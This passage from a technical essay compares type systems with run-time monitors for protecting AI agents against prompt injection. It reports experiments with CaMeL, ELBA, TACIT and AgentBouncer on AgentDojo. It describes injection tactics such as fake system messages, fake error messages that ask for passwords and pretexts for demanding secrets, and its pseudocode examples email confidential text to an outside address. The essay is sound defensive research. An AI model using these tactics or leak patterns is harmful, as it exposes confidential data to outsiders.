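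CaMeL, a 2025 system by Debenedetti and colleagues, tracks labels through whole scripts. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), a privileged model receives only the user's request and writes a plan in a restricted form of Python. CaMeL's own interpreter runs the plan and makes all the tool calls. When the plan needs to extract information from untrusted text, the interpreter passes the text to a quarantined model, which has no tools. Every value carries a label that records its sources and its permitted readers. Before each tool call, a policy function receives the call, its arguments and their labels, and returns allow or deny.

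In the contracts script, `texts` would have the contracts folder as its source and the firm's staff as its readers, and `summary` would inherit both. The words "The summary is ready." come from the plan itself, so they have no restriction on who may read them.

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) notes that both designs follow a two-model pattern that the programmer Simon Willison described in 2023. They differ mainly in when they plan. CaMeL's privileged model writes its plan before anything reads the data, whereas the model in Fides chooses each call after the previous one and can use any results that Fides hasn't hidden. CaMeL does little to check the plan before running it. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) points out that Python's dynamic types, exceptions and reflection make static analysis difficult, and recommends a language designed for security instead.

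A label affects an action only if a policy tests it, so the monitor's decision depends on which labels the policy tests. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) describes a CaMeL-style program that takes a recipient's address from an untrusted email. The address keeps its untrusted label, but the policy tests only the subject and body, so the message goes out. Costa and colleagues give an example of the opposite policy, which requires a trusted recipient but allows untrusted text in the message. The law firm should choose the second policy, because under the first a sentence in a contract could determine where an email goes.

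Labels on values track data as it moves, but an outsider might also learn something from which actions the assistant takes. Costa and colleagues prove that their label tracking satisfies explicit secrecy, a property that is weaker than noninterference because it doesn't cover such inferences. They argue that enforcing noninterference would in effect mean banning calls that write to public places after any call that might have read secrets, which they consider too restrictive.

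### LIO: one label for the whole computation

LIO, the Haskell library that ELBA uses for requirement B, does impose roughly that ban. Stefan, Russo and colleagues (2012), in *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions*, give the running computation a single current label, which covers everything it has read so far. *On Dynamic Flow-Sensitive Floating-Label Systems* (2015) states the two main rules compactly. If L is the current label, then:

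- reading data with label d changes L to L ⊔ d
- writing to a destination with label e is possible only if L ⊑ e

Here ⊔ combines two labels and ⊑ means "may flow to". If labels are lists of permitted readers, each read can only shorten the current list, and a write succeeds only if everyone who can read the destination is still on that list. LIO is therefore a state machine like the one for requirement C, with the current label as its state.

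When the contracts script starts, its label permits every reader. After it reads the two contracts, the label is {lawyer, partner}. The script can still email the lawyer or save a file that only she can open. If it tries to email an outsider, LIO raises an error whatever the message contains, so it also blocks the email that says "all fine" only when the contracts contain no penalty clause. LIO's two rules thus enforce the strict form of requirement B, except for leaks through whether or when a program finishes. Fides could enforce it only by adopting a similar restriction.

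However, the label never becomes less restrictive by itself, so if the lawyer later asked the same session to book a courier, LIO would block the message to the courier company. Stefan and colleagues deal with this through a function called `toLabeled`, which runs part of the program separately. The label can rise inside that part, but the rest of the program receives a sealed result and keeps its old label unless it opens the result.

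In ELBA, a sub-agent can run inside `toLabeled`, read untrusted text and write a message. The main agent can then pass the sealed message to a tool that checks the message's label. Zhou and colleagues point out that the sub-agent, unlike CaMeL's quarantined model, can use tools itself, because LIO checks each call against the sub-agent's current label.

LIO can also set a clearance, which is an upper limit on the current label. Suppose only the personnel department may read the personnel files. If the clearance requires the lawyer to remain a permitted reader, the script fails as soon as it tries to open one of those files. The clearance limits what the script can read, so it helps with requirement A.

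Although LIO decides at run time, it relies on types to ensure that its checks always happen. As with `BibIO`, a script can't use ordinary Haskell input and output, so it can't write a file without LIO's check. But a script can pass the type checker and still attempt something the policy forbids. Zhou and colleagues give an example that compiles and fetches data from an untrusted website, but LIO stops it when it tries to pass that data to the user.

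Stefan and colleagues acknowledge that static analysis adds less overhead, causes fewer run-time failures and handles leaks through a program's decisions better. They chose run-time labels because new users and new kinds of data can appear while a program is running. In their example of a conference review system, an organiser may discover a conflict of interest halfway through and restrict who can read a review. The review's label can change at that point without anyone recompiling the program.

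### AgentBouncer: system calls and a model for unclear cases

The contracts script calls `summarise`, and a monitor that checks only tool calls does not cover what happens inside that function. *AgentBouncer* (Joos and Pradel, 2026) checks system calls, which are requests from a program to the core of the operating system, for example to open a file, start another program or connect to a network. The operating system holds each relevant call until the monitor allows or denies it. If `summarise` tried to post the contracts to a website, the monitor could block the connection. A proxy unpacks web traffic, so the monitor receives the full address and content of each web request.

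Joos and Pradel built AgentBouncer for software engineering agents, which can run any command they like, so nobody can list in advance everything that a task might require. The monitor reduces each system call to an operation, a resource and, for files, whether the program wants to read or write. It then looks for a verdict in this order:

1. If a language model has already judged the same request during the current task, the earlier verdict applies.
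2. If the request matches a standing rule, the rule applies. The default set contains 60 permissions for routine operations, such as running standard system programs.
3. If the model has approved the whole folder or web address that contains the resource, the request goes ahead.
4. Otherwise the model decides.

In the tests without attacks, an average task produced about 28,000 decisions, and the model made only about eight of them. It receives the user's task, the current tool call, the agent's stated reason for the call and the request itself, and it judges how necessary and how safe the request is. It should deny any unsafe request, even one the task seems to need. If the need is unclear, it should approve the request only when it is confident that the request is safe.

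The same request can therefore get different verdicts in different tasks. Adding a line to a user's shell settings is reasonable if the user asked for a change to those settings, but not if the task is to edit a README file. A fixed list would have to permit the edit in both tasks or forbid it in both.

A denied call fails with an ordinary permission error, which many programs can handle. When the tool finishes, AgentBouncer adds a note about what it denied, so the agent can adjust.

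### Fixed rules and model judgements

A deterministic monitor always gives the same verdict for the same action, policy and recorded state. The policy functions in CaMeL and Fides, LIO's label comparisons and AgentBouncer's standing rules all work this way. So do AgentSpec's conditions, though some of its responses hand the decision to a model or a person. A deterministic rule can still be wrong, for example because a list of the firm's addresses is out of date. But the firm can reproduce the mistake, correct the rule and be sure that the same case won't go wrong again.

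A language model's judgement can be wrong in less predictable ways, and text in its input can influence it. Joos and Pradel keep tool outputs away from the judging model for this reason, but injected text could still reach it through the task description or the agent's explanation. In their tests without attacks, AgentBouncer denied at least one system call in 3.42% of harmless tool calls, but only 0.25% of harmless tool calls failed as a result. In the attack tests, file-listing commands were a common source of false alarms. They look up user names in a system file and print numbers instead if they can't open it. The model also approved some harmful requests, mostly ones that didn't look dangerous on their own, such as reading a file that might be sensitive.

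Joos and Pradel also ran AgentBouncer without the model, so that it denied everything outside the standing rules. It stopped every attack in the test set, but the agent solved only 8.24% of its tasks, compared with 72.94% when the model handled unclear cases. The rules didn't permit the agent to change the files it was supposed to fix. This is strong evidence against using one short, general list of rules for open-ended programming work. It is much weaker evidence against using one for the contracts assistant, which does the same few things every day, and Joos and Pradel accept that fixed rules may be enough for such tasks.

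A language model can't meet Anderson's third condition, because nobody can analyse or test it completely. But a model can write the rules, and ordinary code can apply them to each action. Wang and colleagues tried this with OpenAI's o1 model on household tasks for a robot. Of the actions that the generated rules flagged, 95.56% were hazardous, but the rules caught only 70.96% of all hazardous actions. The rules weren't ready to use alone, though a person could read them and add the missing cases before the robot did anything.

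## What does a guarantee for all inputs add to watching the run that happens?

Most scripts that an AI agent writes run once, on inputs that already exist. A monitor checks that run, while a type checker's guarantee covers every possible run. Nearly all of those other runs will never happen, so ruling out the bad ones adds little when the rule is about which files a script may read. The guarantee adds a lot when the rule is about keeping contracts secret, because what an outsider learns from one run depends on what the script would have done if the contracts had been different.

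### What soundness promises

A sound checker accepts a program only if the policy holds for everything the program could do. In Zhou and colleagues' formula for this, the property *P* is a yes-or-no condition on the whole set of a program's possible traces.

For requirement A, that the assistant reads only the contracts folder, *P* holds if no trace contains a read outside the folder, so each trace can be checked on its own. Checking noninterference, the strict form of requirement B, means comparing traces from runs on different contracts. A single trace therefore can't show whether a program satisfies it, and each trace must also record the inputs that led to it.

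A sound checker can reject any number of harmless scripts. Accepting every script that obeys the policy is a separate property called completeness, which practical type checkers lack.

### From ordinary programs to agents

Soundness proofs usually concern programs that are fully written before they run. An agent's program requests more code from a model as it runs, so part of its text is missing when the compiler first checks it. Zhou and colleagues take a typed language *L* and add an operation, `agent`, that requests a program of a given type from a model, checks the reply and runs it if it passes. They prove that the extended language's type system still enforces every property that *L*'s does.

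The proof turns an agent program into an ordinary one that behaves identically:

1. Replace each `agent` call with a function written in *L*. The function sends the prompt to the model, type-checks the reply and runs it, or returns the value `Nothing` if the check fails.
2. Deal with replies that contain `agent` calls of their own. Every call has a limit on how many further levels of calls it can lead to, and the calls in its reply have lower limits. A call with limit 0 always returns `Nothing`, so its replacement needs no model. The replacement for limit 1 uses only the one for limit 0, the replacement for limit 2 uses only those two, and so on upwards.
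3. Compare the two programs. Each replacement receives the same reply as the call it stands for and applies the same check, so both programs have the same set of traces.
4. Apply the original guarantee. The new program is an ordinary *L* program of the same type, so *P* holds for its traces, and those are also the traces of the agent program.

This argument holds whatever code the model writes, so it covers a hostile model as well as a careless one. But Haskell's types can't enforce a rule on an agent's code if they can't enforce it on code that people write.

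The theorem assumes that the model always gives the same reply to the same request, which real models don't do. Zhou and colleagues consider this variation irrelevant to the policies they study, and suggest reusing stored replies where it matters. The variation could matter for noninterference, since two runs might differ by chance even if no secret influenced them. *The LLMbda Calculus* instead treats each model call as a random draw, and Zhou and colleagues credit it with a formal proof of noninterference.

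The other assumptions are easier to meet. Nested calls must have some limit, *L* has to let a running program type-check and run new code, and developers have to write the whole application in *L*. A trace contains only tool calls with an observable side effect, so the theorem doesn't cover leaks through a script's running time.

Under the formal definition, a type system's guarantee can also depend on a run-time monitor. In ELBA, every trace of a well-typed script obeys requirement B only because the LIO library stops the script at run time before it can violate the requirement.

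### Which policies can each method enforce?

Schneider worked out the limits of a monitor that can only observe a program's steps and halt it. A policy has to meet three conditions before such a monitor can enforce it:

- The policy judges each trace by itself, without comparing it with others.
- If an unfinished trace breaks the policy, every continuation of it does too. The program might end at that point, so the monitor can't count on later actions to put things right.
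- Every trace that breaks the policy does so after a finite number of steps.

Policies that meet all three conditions are safety properties, which require that some bad thing never happens. Requirements A and C (at most one email) are safety properties. Requirement E, that a summary eventually arrives, fails the third condition. It would pass with a deadline, because "a summary arrives within ten minutes" has a definite moment of failure.

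Noninterference fails the first condition. Schneider argues that removing traces from a harmless set can produce a harmful one. Suppose a script tosses a coin and emails an outsider "yes" or "no" depending on the result. The contracts either contain a penalty clause or don't, so there are four possible traces, and the outsider learns nothing about the clause from the email. Now remove the trace with a clause and a "no", and the trace without a clause and a "yes". In the two that remain, the outsider receives "yes" exactly when the contracts contain the clause. Both traces also belonged to the harmless set, so no test of single traces could accept the first set and reject the second.

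A halting monitor can therefore only enforce a policy stricter than noninterference, such as Schneider's ban on sending any message after reading a file. The editing monitors of Ligatti and colleagues can enforce some policies beyond safety, such as the rule about the client register, but in their theory a policy still applies to one trace at a time.

*Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, 2006) added static checks to the comparison. It defines a static check as a procedure that reads a program's text and always gives the correct answer in finite time, so static checks can enforce exactly the decidable policies. "The program stops within 100 steps" is decidable because a program can read at most 100 symbols of input in 100 steps, so the procedure can try every input of that length. "The program never writes to the disk's boot sector" is undecidable,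 but a monitor can enforce it by stopping the program when it is about to write there.

In this model, monitors are strictly more powerful than static checks. A monitor could even run the static check as soon as the program loads. But the result assumes that both methods have the same information, including the program's text. Many agent monitors have much less information. AgentBouncer, for example, works from system calls and doesn't analyse the script that caused them. Hamlen and colleagues note that when the two methods work from different information, each may enforce policies that the other can't.

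Later work corrected the earlier theory, which overstated what monitors can enforce. A monitor can enforce a policy only if it has a response that doesn't itself break that policy. For example, a monitor that can only halt the script can't enforce a rule that the script must keep running.

A monitor also has to act in time. Hamlen and colleagues describe a service that lends a resource to one program at a time and can't take it back. When a program declares that it has finished with the resource, the monitor has to decide whether this is true before the service lends the resource to another program. The monitor can't tell from the trace so far, because the answer depends on what the program will do next. A static check can answer conservatively. For example, TACIT forbids any value from carrying a file-system capability out of its block, so the compiler establishes before the script runs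 that it can't use the capability after the block ends.

Program rewriting, which changes a program before it runs, can enforce some policies that neither static checks nor monitors can. The rewritten program must obey the policy, and if the original already obeyed it, the two must behave equivalently. Suppose a folder contains a file whose existence is secret, and every program must behave as if the file weren't there. Deciding whether a program complies is as hard as deciding whether two arbitrary programs are equivalent. A rewriter doesn't need to decide this, because it can change the command that lists the folder so that the listing omits the file. Programs that ignored the file behave as before, and the rest can no longer react to it.

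Hamlen and colleagues' examples sort as follows, where "yes" means that the method can enforce the policy exactly:

| Policy | Static check | Monitor | Rewriting |
|---|---|---|---|
| The program stops within 100 steps | yes | yes | yes |
| The program never writes to the boot sector | no | yes | yes |
| The program behaves as if the secret file did not exist | no | no | yes |
| The program stops on at least one input | no | no | no |

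### Why a sound checker rejects harmless scripts

A static check can still prevent violations of an undecidable policy if it is allowed to reject some harmless code. The following script shows why such rejections are unavoidable. The function `halts_within(p, n)` simulates the first `n` steps of another program, `p`, and returns true if `p` has stopped by then.

```
n = 0
while true:
    n = n + 1
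    if halts_within(p, n):
        send_email("someone@elsewhere.example", texts[0])
```

The forbidden email goes out if and only if `p` eventually stops. A checker that gave the right answer for every `p` could decide whether any given program stops, and Alan Turing showed in 1936 that no procedure can do that. A sound checker therefore has to reject the script for some programs `p` that run forever, and in practice it rejects the script for all of them. A monitor can let the loop run and block the email if the script ever tries to send it.

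Few scripts written for a law firm will depend on an undecidable question. Type checkers mostly reject harmless code because they don't predict which branch will run, as already seen with capture sets. Sabelfeld and Russo, who compared type systems with monitors for secrecy, give the example of a program that copies a secret into a public variable if *l* > *l*. The copy never happens, because no number is greater than itself, but their type system still rejects the program.

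### A single run under an access rule

Suppose the contracts script also opens the personnel folder whenever a contract names an employee, and it runs once, under a monitor that intercepts every read. If no contract names an employee, the script doesn't try to open the folder. If one does, the monitor blocks the read before any data moves. The personnel files stay closed in both cases, which is enough to meet requirement A for this run.

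A type checker that limits the script to the contracts folder would have rejected it because of what it might do with other contracts. If today's contracts name no employee, the lawyer would have waited for a second script even though the first could have produced the summary. The guarantee for all inputs makes this run no safer. The same is true of requirement C, which a monitor can enforce just by recording whether the script has already sent an email. Hamlen and colleagues add that some policies are simpler to enforce with a monitor even when a static check could enforce them, which leaves less room for mistakes in the mechanism.

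Odersky and colleagues say that types give guarantees for all inputs. This is a weak reason to prefer types for access rules on throwaway scripts, but a much better one when the rule concerns secrecy.

### A leak through an if-statement

Suppose a script has searched the contracts and set `has_penalty` to true or false. It continues:

```
report = "penalty clause"
seen   = false
if has_penalty:  seen = true
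if not seen:     report = "no penalty clause"
send_email("someone@elsewhere.example", report)
```

The outsider always learns the right answer from the email, although the script never copies any contract text into it. The information moves through the choice of branch, which makes this an implicit flow. Copying `texts[0]` into `report` would be an explicit flow.

Imagine a monitor that labels a variable each time the script assigns to it. The label is "confidential" if the new value comes from confidential data, or if the assignment is inside a branch whose condition is confidential. Otherwise the label is "public". The monitor misses the leak whatever the contracts contain:

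| Part of the script | Contracts with a penalty clause | Contracts without one |
|---|---|---|
| first two lines | `report` and `seen` are public | `report` and `seen` are public |
| `if has_penalty` | runs the assignment, so `seen` becomes confidential | skips the assignment, so `seen` stays public |
| `if not seen` | skips the assignment, so `report` stays public | runs the assignment under a public condition, so `report` stays public |
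| `send_email` | allowed: "penalty clause" | allowed: "no penalty clause" |

The mistake in the right-hand column comes at `if has_penalty`. The variable `seen` is still false because there is no penalty clause, so its value reveals confidential information, but the assignment that would have changed its label didn't run. A type checker for information flow examines both branches. It marks `seen` as confidential after the first `if` whatever the contracts contain, does the same to `report` after the second, and rejects the email. TACIT would reject the script at the first `if`, because `has_penalty` would be wrapped.

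Monitors can handle implicit flows in some languages. Sabelfeld and Russo, in *From dynamic to static and back* (2009), compared a standard type system with a monitor for a small language in which every variable keeps one label throughout. The type system forbids assignments to public variables inside a branch with a secret condition. The monitor tracks the conditions of the branches the program is currently inside, and stops the program before it makes such an assignment. Sabelfeld and Russo proved that both give the same secrecy guarantee. The monitor is also strictly more permissive, because it lets every run of a well-typed program proceed and also accepts harmless programs that the type system rejects, such as the one that tests whether *l* > *l*.

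Both the monitor and the type system guarantee termination-insensitive noninterference, which doesn't cover what an observer can infer from a program's failure to finish. If `seen` has a fixed public label, the monitor stops the script at `seen = true` when there is a penalty clause. When there isn't one, the script sends the email "no penalty clause". The outsider can therefore tell whether there is a penalty clause by whether the email arrives. The type system leaves the same gap, since it accepts a loop that runs forever if `has_penalty` is true.

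Sabelfeld and Russo consider this leak tolerable because it is slow. A program with unrestricted implicit flows can reveal a long secret bit by bit in a loop, but a program that has stopped can't go on to the next bit. Their argument applies only to a single program, though, and an agent can write many. Under either method, a hostile model could put one yes-or-no question about the contracts into each script and learn the answer from whether the script finished.

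Fixed labels are also inconvenient, because a variable that holds contract text early in a script may hold a harmless file name later. A practical system should let the variable's label change. Russo and Sabelfeld, in *Dynamic vs. Static Flow-Sensitive Security Analysis* (2010), proved that the monitor loses its advantage when labels can change. No purely dynamic monitor can be sound and also allow everything that a standard type system with changing labels accepts. They call a monitor purely dynamic if its decisions don't depend on instructions the program hasn't reached yet or on branches it doesn't take.

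Two harmless variants of the script above are enough for the proof. In variant 1, the body of the second `if` is empty, so the email always reads "penalty clause". In variant 2, the body of the first `if` is empty, so the email always reads "no penalty clause". Neither email depends on the contracts. The type system accepts both variants, so the monitor has to let both run.

On contracts with a penalty clause, the original script differs from variant 1 only in a branch that the run skips, so a purely dynamic monitor must allow the run. On contracts without a penalty clause, the script differs from variant 2 only in a branch that the run skips, so the monitor must allow that run too. The two runs send different emails, so a recipient can tell whether the contracts have a penalty clause.

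Given the theorem, a system that decides at run time has several options. LIO blocks harmless emails as well as harmful ones, and Fides enforces a weaker property than noninterference.

Russo and Sabelfeld describe a third option, a hybrid monitor that also reads the branches a program skips. When the script passes an `if` with a confidential condition, the hybrid marks as confidential every variable that the skipped branch could have changed. In the script above, `seen` becomes confidential whether or not there is a penalty clause. The second `if` then makes `report` confidential, and the monitor stops the email. Russo and Sabelfeld prove that such hybrids give the same termination-insensitive guarantee as the type system and accept more than it does. If a script puts contract text into a message only when a public variable `urgent` is true, the type system rejects the script outright, whereas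 the hybrid lets it send the message when `urgent` is false.

Keeping data secret requires some analysis of the code that doesn't run, even if the script runs only once. A compiler can do this analysis before the run, or a monitor that can read the script can do it during the run. A monitor that receives only a list of tool calls can't do it, so it has to block too much or miss some leaks.

### Code that the agent keeps

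Some generated code is used again after the run it was written for. In LACUNA, Zhao and colleagues let a program ask the model for a function instead of a single result. In one example, the program asks for a function that turns whole numbers into Roman numerals. The model writes it once, the compiler checks it once, and the program can then call it any number of times. An agent can build a library of such functions and replace an old one by defining a new one with the same name and type.

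Each later call to the code brings inputs that didn't exist when the model wrote it, so a guarantee for all inputs covers runs that will happen. Zhao and colleagues give an example in which the model has to name a colour that can be red, green or blue, and its code handles only red and green. Every run on red or green would succeed, but the compiler rejects the code at once and reports that blue is missing.

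For access rules, a guarantee for all inputs mainly adds reliability. Suppose the firm keeps a summarising function that opens a forbidden folder only when a contract refers to a side letter. A monitor would keep that folder closed every time, but the function might work for six months and then stop in the middle of an urgent job. Hamlen and colleagues point out that a monitor may signal a violation arbitrarily late and only on some runs. A static check would have exposed the problem on the first day, while the model was still available to fix it. For code the firm keeps, the advantage of a monitor is that a new rule applies from the next call, whereas a new rule expressed in types doesn't affect an old function until someone recompiles it.

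The guarantee also covers only what the type expresses, and Zhao and colleagues note that well-typed code isn't necessarily correct. The request for Roman numerals covered 1 to 3999, but the function's type allows any whole number. The generated code compiles, but given 4000, it returns "MMMM", which isn't a standard numeral.

### Stopping before the first effect

In an example from LACUNA, a type error in the second line of a snippet prevented the first line from subtracting 50 from an account balance. This protection matters even for code that runs once, and it also applies when the error concerns permissions. Suppose a script saves a summary, emails a contract to a stranger and then tells the lawyer that the summary is ready. A monitor that halts the script at the forbidden email leaves a saved summary that the lawyer hasn't been told about. If a compiler rejects the script, nothing has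 been saved yet, and the next attempt starts from the original state.

Retrying is safe when the failed code hasn't changed anything. If an interpreter subtracts 50 from an account balance, fails on the next line and then runs a corrected version of the whole snippet, the account loses 100. ELBA automatically prompts the model for new code after a type error, when the rejected code hasn't yet made any tool calls, but not after a run-time error.

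A monitor can imitate some of this by saving the old balance and restoring it after a failure, or by holding back file changes until the script has finished. Hamlen and colleagues mention the need for such rollback as a disadvantage of discovering violations late. Rollback works for variables and files on the firm's own machines, but not for an email that has already been sent. Checking first therefore has the greatest advantage for scripts that mix several actions, at least one of which can't be undone.

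The guarantee applies only to violations that the types can detect. In ELBA, a script that tries to email contract text to a stranger can save a file before LIO stops the email, and the file remains.

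## How did typed and monitored agents fare when they were attacked?

In the published attack tests, TACIT, ELBA and CaMeL stopped almost every attack, including some that succeeded when researchers switched the protection off. The tests provide much less evidence about how types compare with monitors, because none ran both on the same agent under the same policy. The systems differed more in utility (the share of legitimate tasks an agent completes) than in the share of attacks they stopped.

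### Secrets in a project folder

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT's main promise, that confidential text never reaches the agent's output. They gave the agent a small Scala project with a secrets folder containing API keys, a database and confidential documents. A hosted model wrote the scripts but was not allowed to see the secrets, while a trusted local model could read them.

The test had 12 legitimate tasks. Some had nothing to do with the secrets, such as listing the API endpoints in a README file, and others required them, such as summarising a confidential incident report. The researchers combined each task with each of 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. The simplest injections were notes or code comments telling the agent to print the secrets. More elaborate ones imitated system messages, faked an error that only a password could fix, claimed that the secrets were test data,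 or supplied Scala code that would read the files. In another 11 trials, the user was the attacker, asking for secrets outright in five and using a pretext, such as an administrator's emergency, in six.

Two models each ran all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets in TACIT's `Classified` wrapper and once with them as ordinary strings. Any secret content in the agent's output counted as a leak. The utility scores cover only the 120 trials with legitimate tasks.

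| Model | Form of the secrets | Leaks from injections | Leaks from malicious requests | Overall leak rate | Utility |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | wrapped | 0 of 120 | 0 of 11 | 0% | 99.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | plain | 0 of 120 | 2 of 11 | 1.5% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | wrapped | 0 of 120 | 0 of 11 | 0% | 90.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | plain | 3 of 120 | 8 of 11 | 8.4% | 88.3% |

The wrapper made the biggest difference when the user asked MiniMax for the secrets, and only a small difference against injections. Sonnet resisted every injection even with plain strings, so the compiler may have had little to stop in its wrapped trials. Zero leaks in 131 trials is also compatible with a true leak rate of about 2%. The main reason to expect no leaks is the argument from the types, and the trials are mostly a check for obvious holes in the implementation.

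Sonnet completed more tasks with the wrapper than without it, but Odersky and colleagues suspect that this is an artifact of the experimental set-up. The model often ran out of turns or time, and it sometimes stopped to warn the user when it noticed an injection.

The version with plain strings had no monitor checking for secrets. A monitor that tracks labels, as CaMeL and Fides do, could also have checked what the agent was about to print. Even the wrapped version relies partly on a run-time measure, since TACIT replaces confidential text with a placeholder when a script prints it. The experiment therefore shows that the wrapper is better than relying on the model's judgement, but it can't show that types are better than monitoring.

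### TACIT and CaMeL on AgentDojo

AgentDojo is a 2024 benchmark that plants prompt injections in the data an agent reads while it does simulated office work, banking, Slack messaging and travel booking. Its lead author, Debenedetti, also led the work on CaMeL. The benchmark pairs each user task with every attacker goal in the same domain. *SecOPD* (2026) counts 949 such pairs in version 1.2.1: 560 in the office workspace, 144 in banking, 140 in travel and 105 in Slack. AgentDojo scores the user's task and the attacker's goal separately, so an agent can complete both in one trial.

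Odersky and colleagues moved all four domains to TACIT without changing the tasks or attacks. They used the two models below because CaMeL's evaluation had used them, and copied CaMeL's results from its paper instead of rerunning it. The table gives utility under attack.

| Domain | CaMeL, Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT, Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL, o4-mini-high | TACIT, o4-mini-high |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 62.5% | 59.0% |
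| Workspace | 53.8% | 50.5% | 81.4% | 52.9% |
| Slack | 48.6% | 40.0% | 68.6% | 47.6% |
| Travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 74.3% | 68.6% |

In about 1,900 trials, AgentDojo counted one successful attack against each system, CaMeL's in banking and TACIT's in travel, both with o4-mini-high.

In TACIT's case, the user asked the agent to book a particular hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for a different one in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel, but it also quoted the reviews word for word. AgentDojo checks the output for the name of the attacker's hotel, so it scored the trial as a success for the attacker. Odersky and colleagues say this isn't a hole in the type system, because the policy lets the user see public reviews. That seems right, but the planted recommendation could still mislead the user, and types that control where text goes can't prevent that.

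If each trial counts equally, CaMeL completed about 76% of the tasks with o4-mini-high and TACIT about 56%. Odersky and colleagues describe the two systems' utility as comparable, which is generous to TACIT for this model. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT leads by about 52% to 45%, but the whole lead comes from the travel domain. In the other three domains together, CaMeL is slightly ahead, by about 53% to 50%.

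CaMeL's 1.4% on travel with Gemini corresponds to two completed tasks in 140 trials, and Odersky and colleagues reprint it without comment. The result looks like a fault in one combination of model and task set rather than a general limit of CaMeL's design. CaMeL completed 74.3% of the same trials with o4-mini-high, and about half of the trials in the other domains with Gemini. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) tested the same Gemini model on another benchmark, AssetOpsBench, where it completed 75.9% of tasks without CaMeL and 55.4% with it, a much smaller loss. The travel result should count for little in the comparison unless someone reproduces it.

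AgentDojo also understates every system's utility under attack. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) gives the example of a user who asks the agent to pay a bill stored in a file. The injection overwrites the payment details in that file, so no agent could complete the task, even if it resisted the attack.

The TACIT version of AgentDojo seems to relax the rule that only pure functions may touch confidential text. Its functions for sending money and email don't require a capability, and according to the agent's instructions, any side effect inside `map` happens immediately. Some relaxation was probably necessary, because an agent can't pay a bill if the amount has to stay inside the wrapper. But if scripts could act from inside `map`, something other than capture checking stopped the attacks. They more likely failed because the injected text never reached the model writing the scripts. It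 doesn't reach CaMeL's planning model either, so these results mainly support a feature the two designs share.

Zhao and colleagues, from the same laboratory, later ran the AgentDojo attacks against LACUNA, using the same two models. Eight attacks succeeded in about 1,900 trials: four in the workspace, three in Slack and one in travel. Utility ranged from 43% to 71% across the domains, much like TACIT's. They explain that the types limit which tools a script can use, but don't stop an attacker from getting the model to misuse a tool that the task requires. For example, the contracts assistant must be able to email the lawyer. If its model could read the contracts, a sentence planted in one might cause it to send her a false statement, and the script would still have the correct type.

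### ELBA and CaMeL on the Slack tasks

Zhou and colleagues ran ELBA and CaMeL themselves on AgentDojo's Slack domain, using four newer models. Pairing the domain's 21 user tasks with its five attacker goals gives 105 combinations, and they worded the attacks three ways. They tested each system with its information-flow policies on and off.

No attack succeeded against CaMeL or ELBA, even with the policies off, so the attacks were too weak to show what the policies do. Without the policies, CaMeL still kept the planning model away from untrusted text, and ELBA still used separate sub-agents to read data. The experiment doesn't show how much of the resistance came from this separation and how much from the models themselves.

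The policies did affect how much work got done. These are the tasks completed when nobody attacked:

| Model | ELBA, policies off | ELBA, policies on | CaMeL, policies off | CaMeL, policies on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 18 of 21 | 10 of 21 | 15 of 21 | 5 of 21 |
| Opus 4.8 | 16 of 21 | 9 of 21 | 16 of 21 | 6 of 21 |
| GPT 5.4 | 16 of 21 | 10 of 21 | 17 of 21 | 5 of 21 |
| Sonnet 5 | 14 of 21 | 8 of 21 | 13 of 21 | 4 of 21 |
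| Total | 64 of 84 | 37 of 84 | 61 of 84 | 20 of 84 |

ELBA and CaMeL did about equally well with their policies off, but ELBA completed nearly twice as many tasks with them on. Although the numbers for each model are small, ELBA also did better in the trials with attacks, where it completed between 40 and 52 of the 105 pairs with its policies on, depending on the model and the wording, and CaMeL completed between 22 and 30.

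Zhou and colleagues attribute CaMeL's lower utility to its fixed plan, whereas an ELBA agent can read a message before deciding which tool to use. This explanation is plausible for tasks such as following instructions in a Slack message, where the right action depends on what the message says.

However, the two systems didn't enforce the same policies. Zhou and colleagues wrote a new policy for ELBA, under which a model that reads untrusted data drops to the privilege level of the data's source. Part of ELBA's advantage could come from this policy rather than its architecture. They propose that future benchmarks use standard policies across systems, which would show whether it does.

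CaMeL and ELBA's LIO library both check labels at run time, so the Slack tasks compared two monitors, one of which is embedded in a typed language. Even a perfectly matched test of these two systems wouldn't compare types with monitoring.

### When the model obeys the attacker

Since the ordinary attacks all failed, Zhou and colleagues simulated a successful one. They changed ELBA so that when a sub-agent received text containing an injection, that text replaced its whole prompt, including its original task. They ran each of the 105 pairs seven times, for 735 trials per model.

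| Model | Injections resisted, policies off | Injections resisted, policies on | Tasks completed, policies off | Tasks completed, policies on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 425 | 735 | 523 | 351 |
| Opus 4.8 | 460 | 735 | 557 | 312 |
| GPT 5.4 | 621 | 735 | 558 | 338 |
| Sonnet 5 | 540 | 735 | 494 | 294 |

Between 16% and 42% of the injections succeeded with the policies off, and none succeeded with them on, after the researchers corrected AgentDojo's results by hand. AgentDojo had counted 29 of the 2,940 runs as successful attacks because the agent opened a certain web address. The researchers reviewed all 29 and found no violation, since the address was fixed and carried no private data.

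The agents completed between 67% and 76% of their tasks with the policies off, but only between 40% and 48% with them on. The policies block some harmless actions, such as writing to a channel after reading an untrusted message, because the label check can't distinguish them from harmful ones. Zhou and colleagues argue that a strict check can still be useful as a filter, because a person needs to review only the actions it blocks.

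The 735 out of 735 result is good evidence for combining static types with runtime monitoring, but not for static checking alone. ELBA type-checked every script in both versions, and many attacks still got through when the policies were off. With the policies on, the types ensured that no script could bypass LIO, and LIO refused the forbidden actions at run time. The result doesn't show whether a type system could have enforced the same policies alone, or how much utility would be lost.

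The citation test is the only ELBA experiment in which static types themselves enforced the rule. The typed agent hallucinated nothing, but nobody was attacking it, so the result concerns accidental errors.

The forced-compromise test didn't include CaMeL. Zhou and colleagues expect it would have blocked these injections too, because its tool calls don't depend on the content of the data. The test also used AgentDojo's existing injections, whereas a real attacker who controlled a sub-agent could look for harmful actions that the policies allow.

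### Repeat runs and stronger attacks

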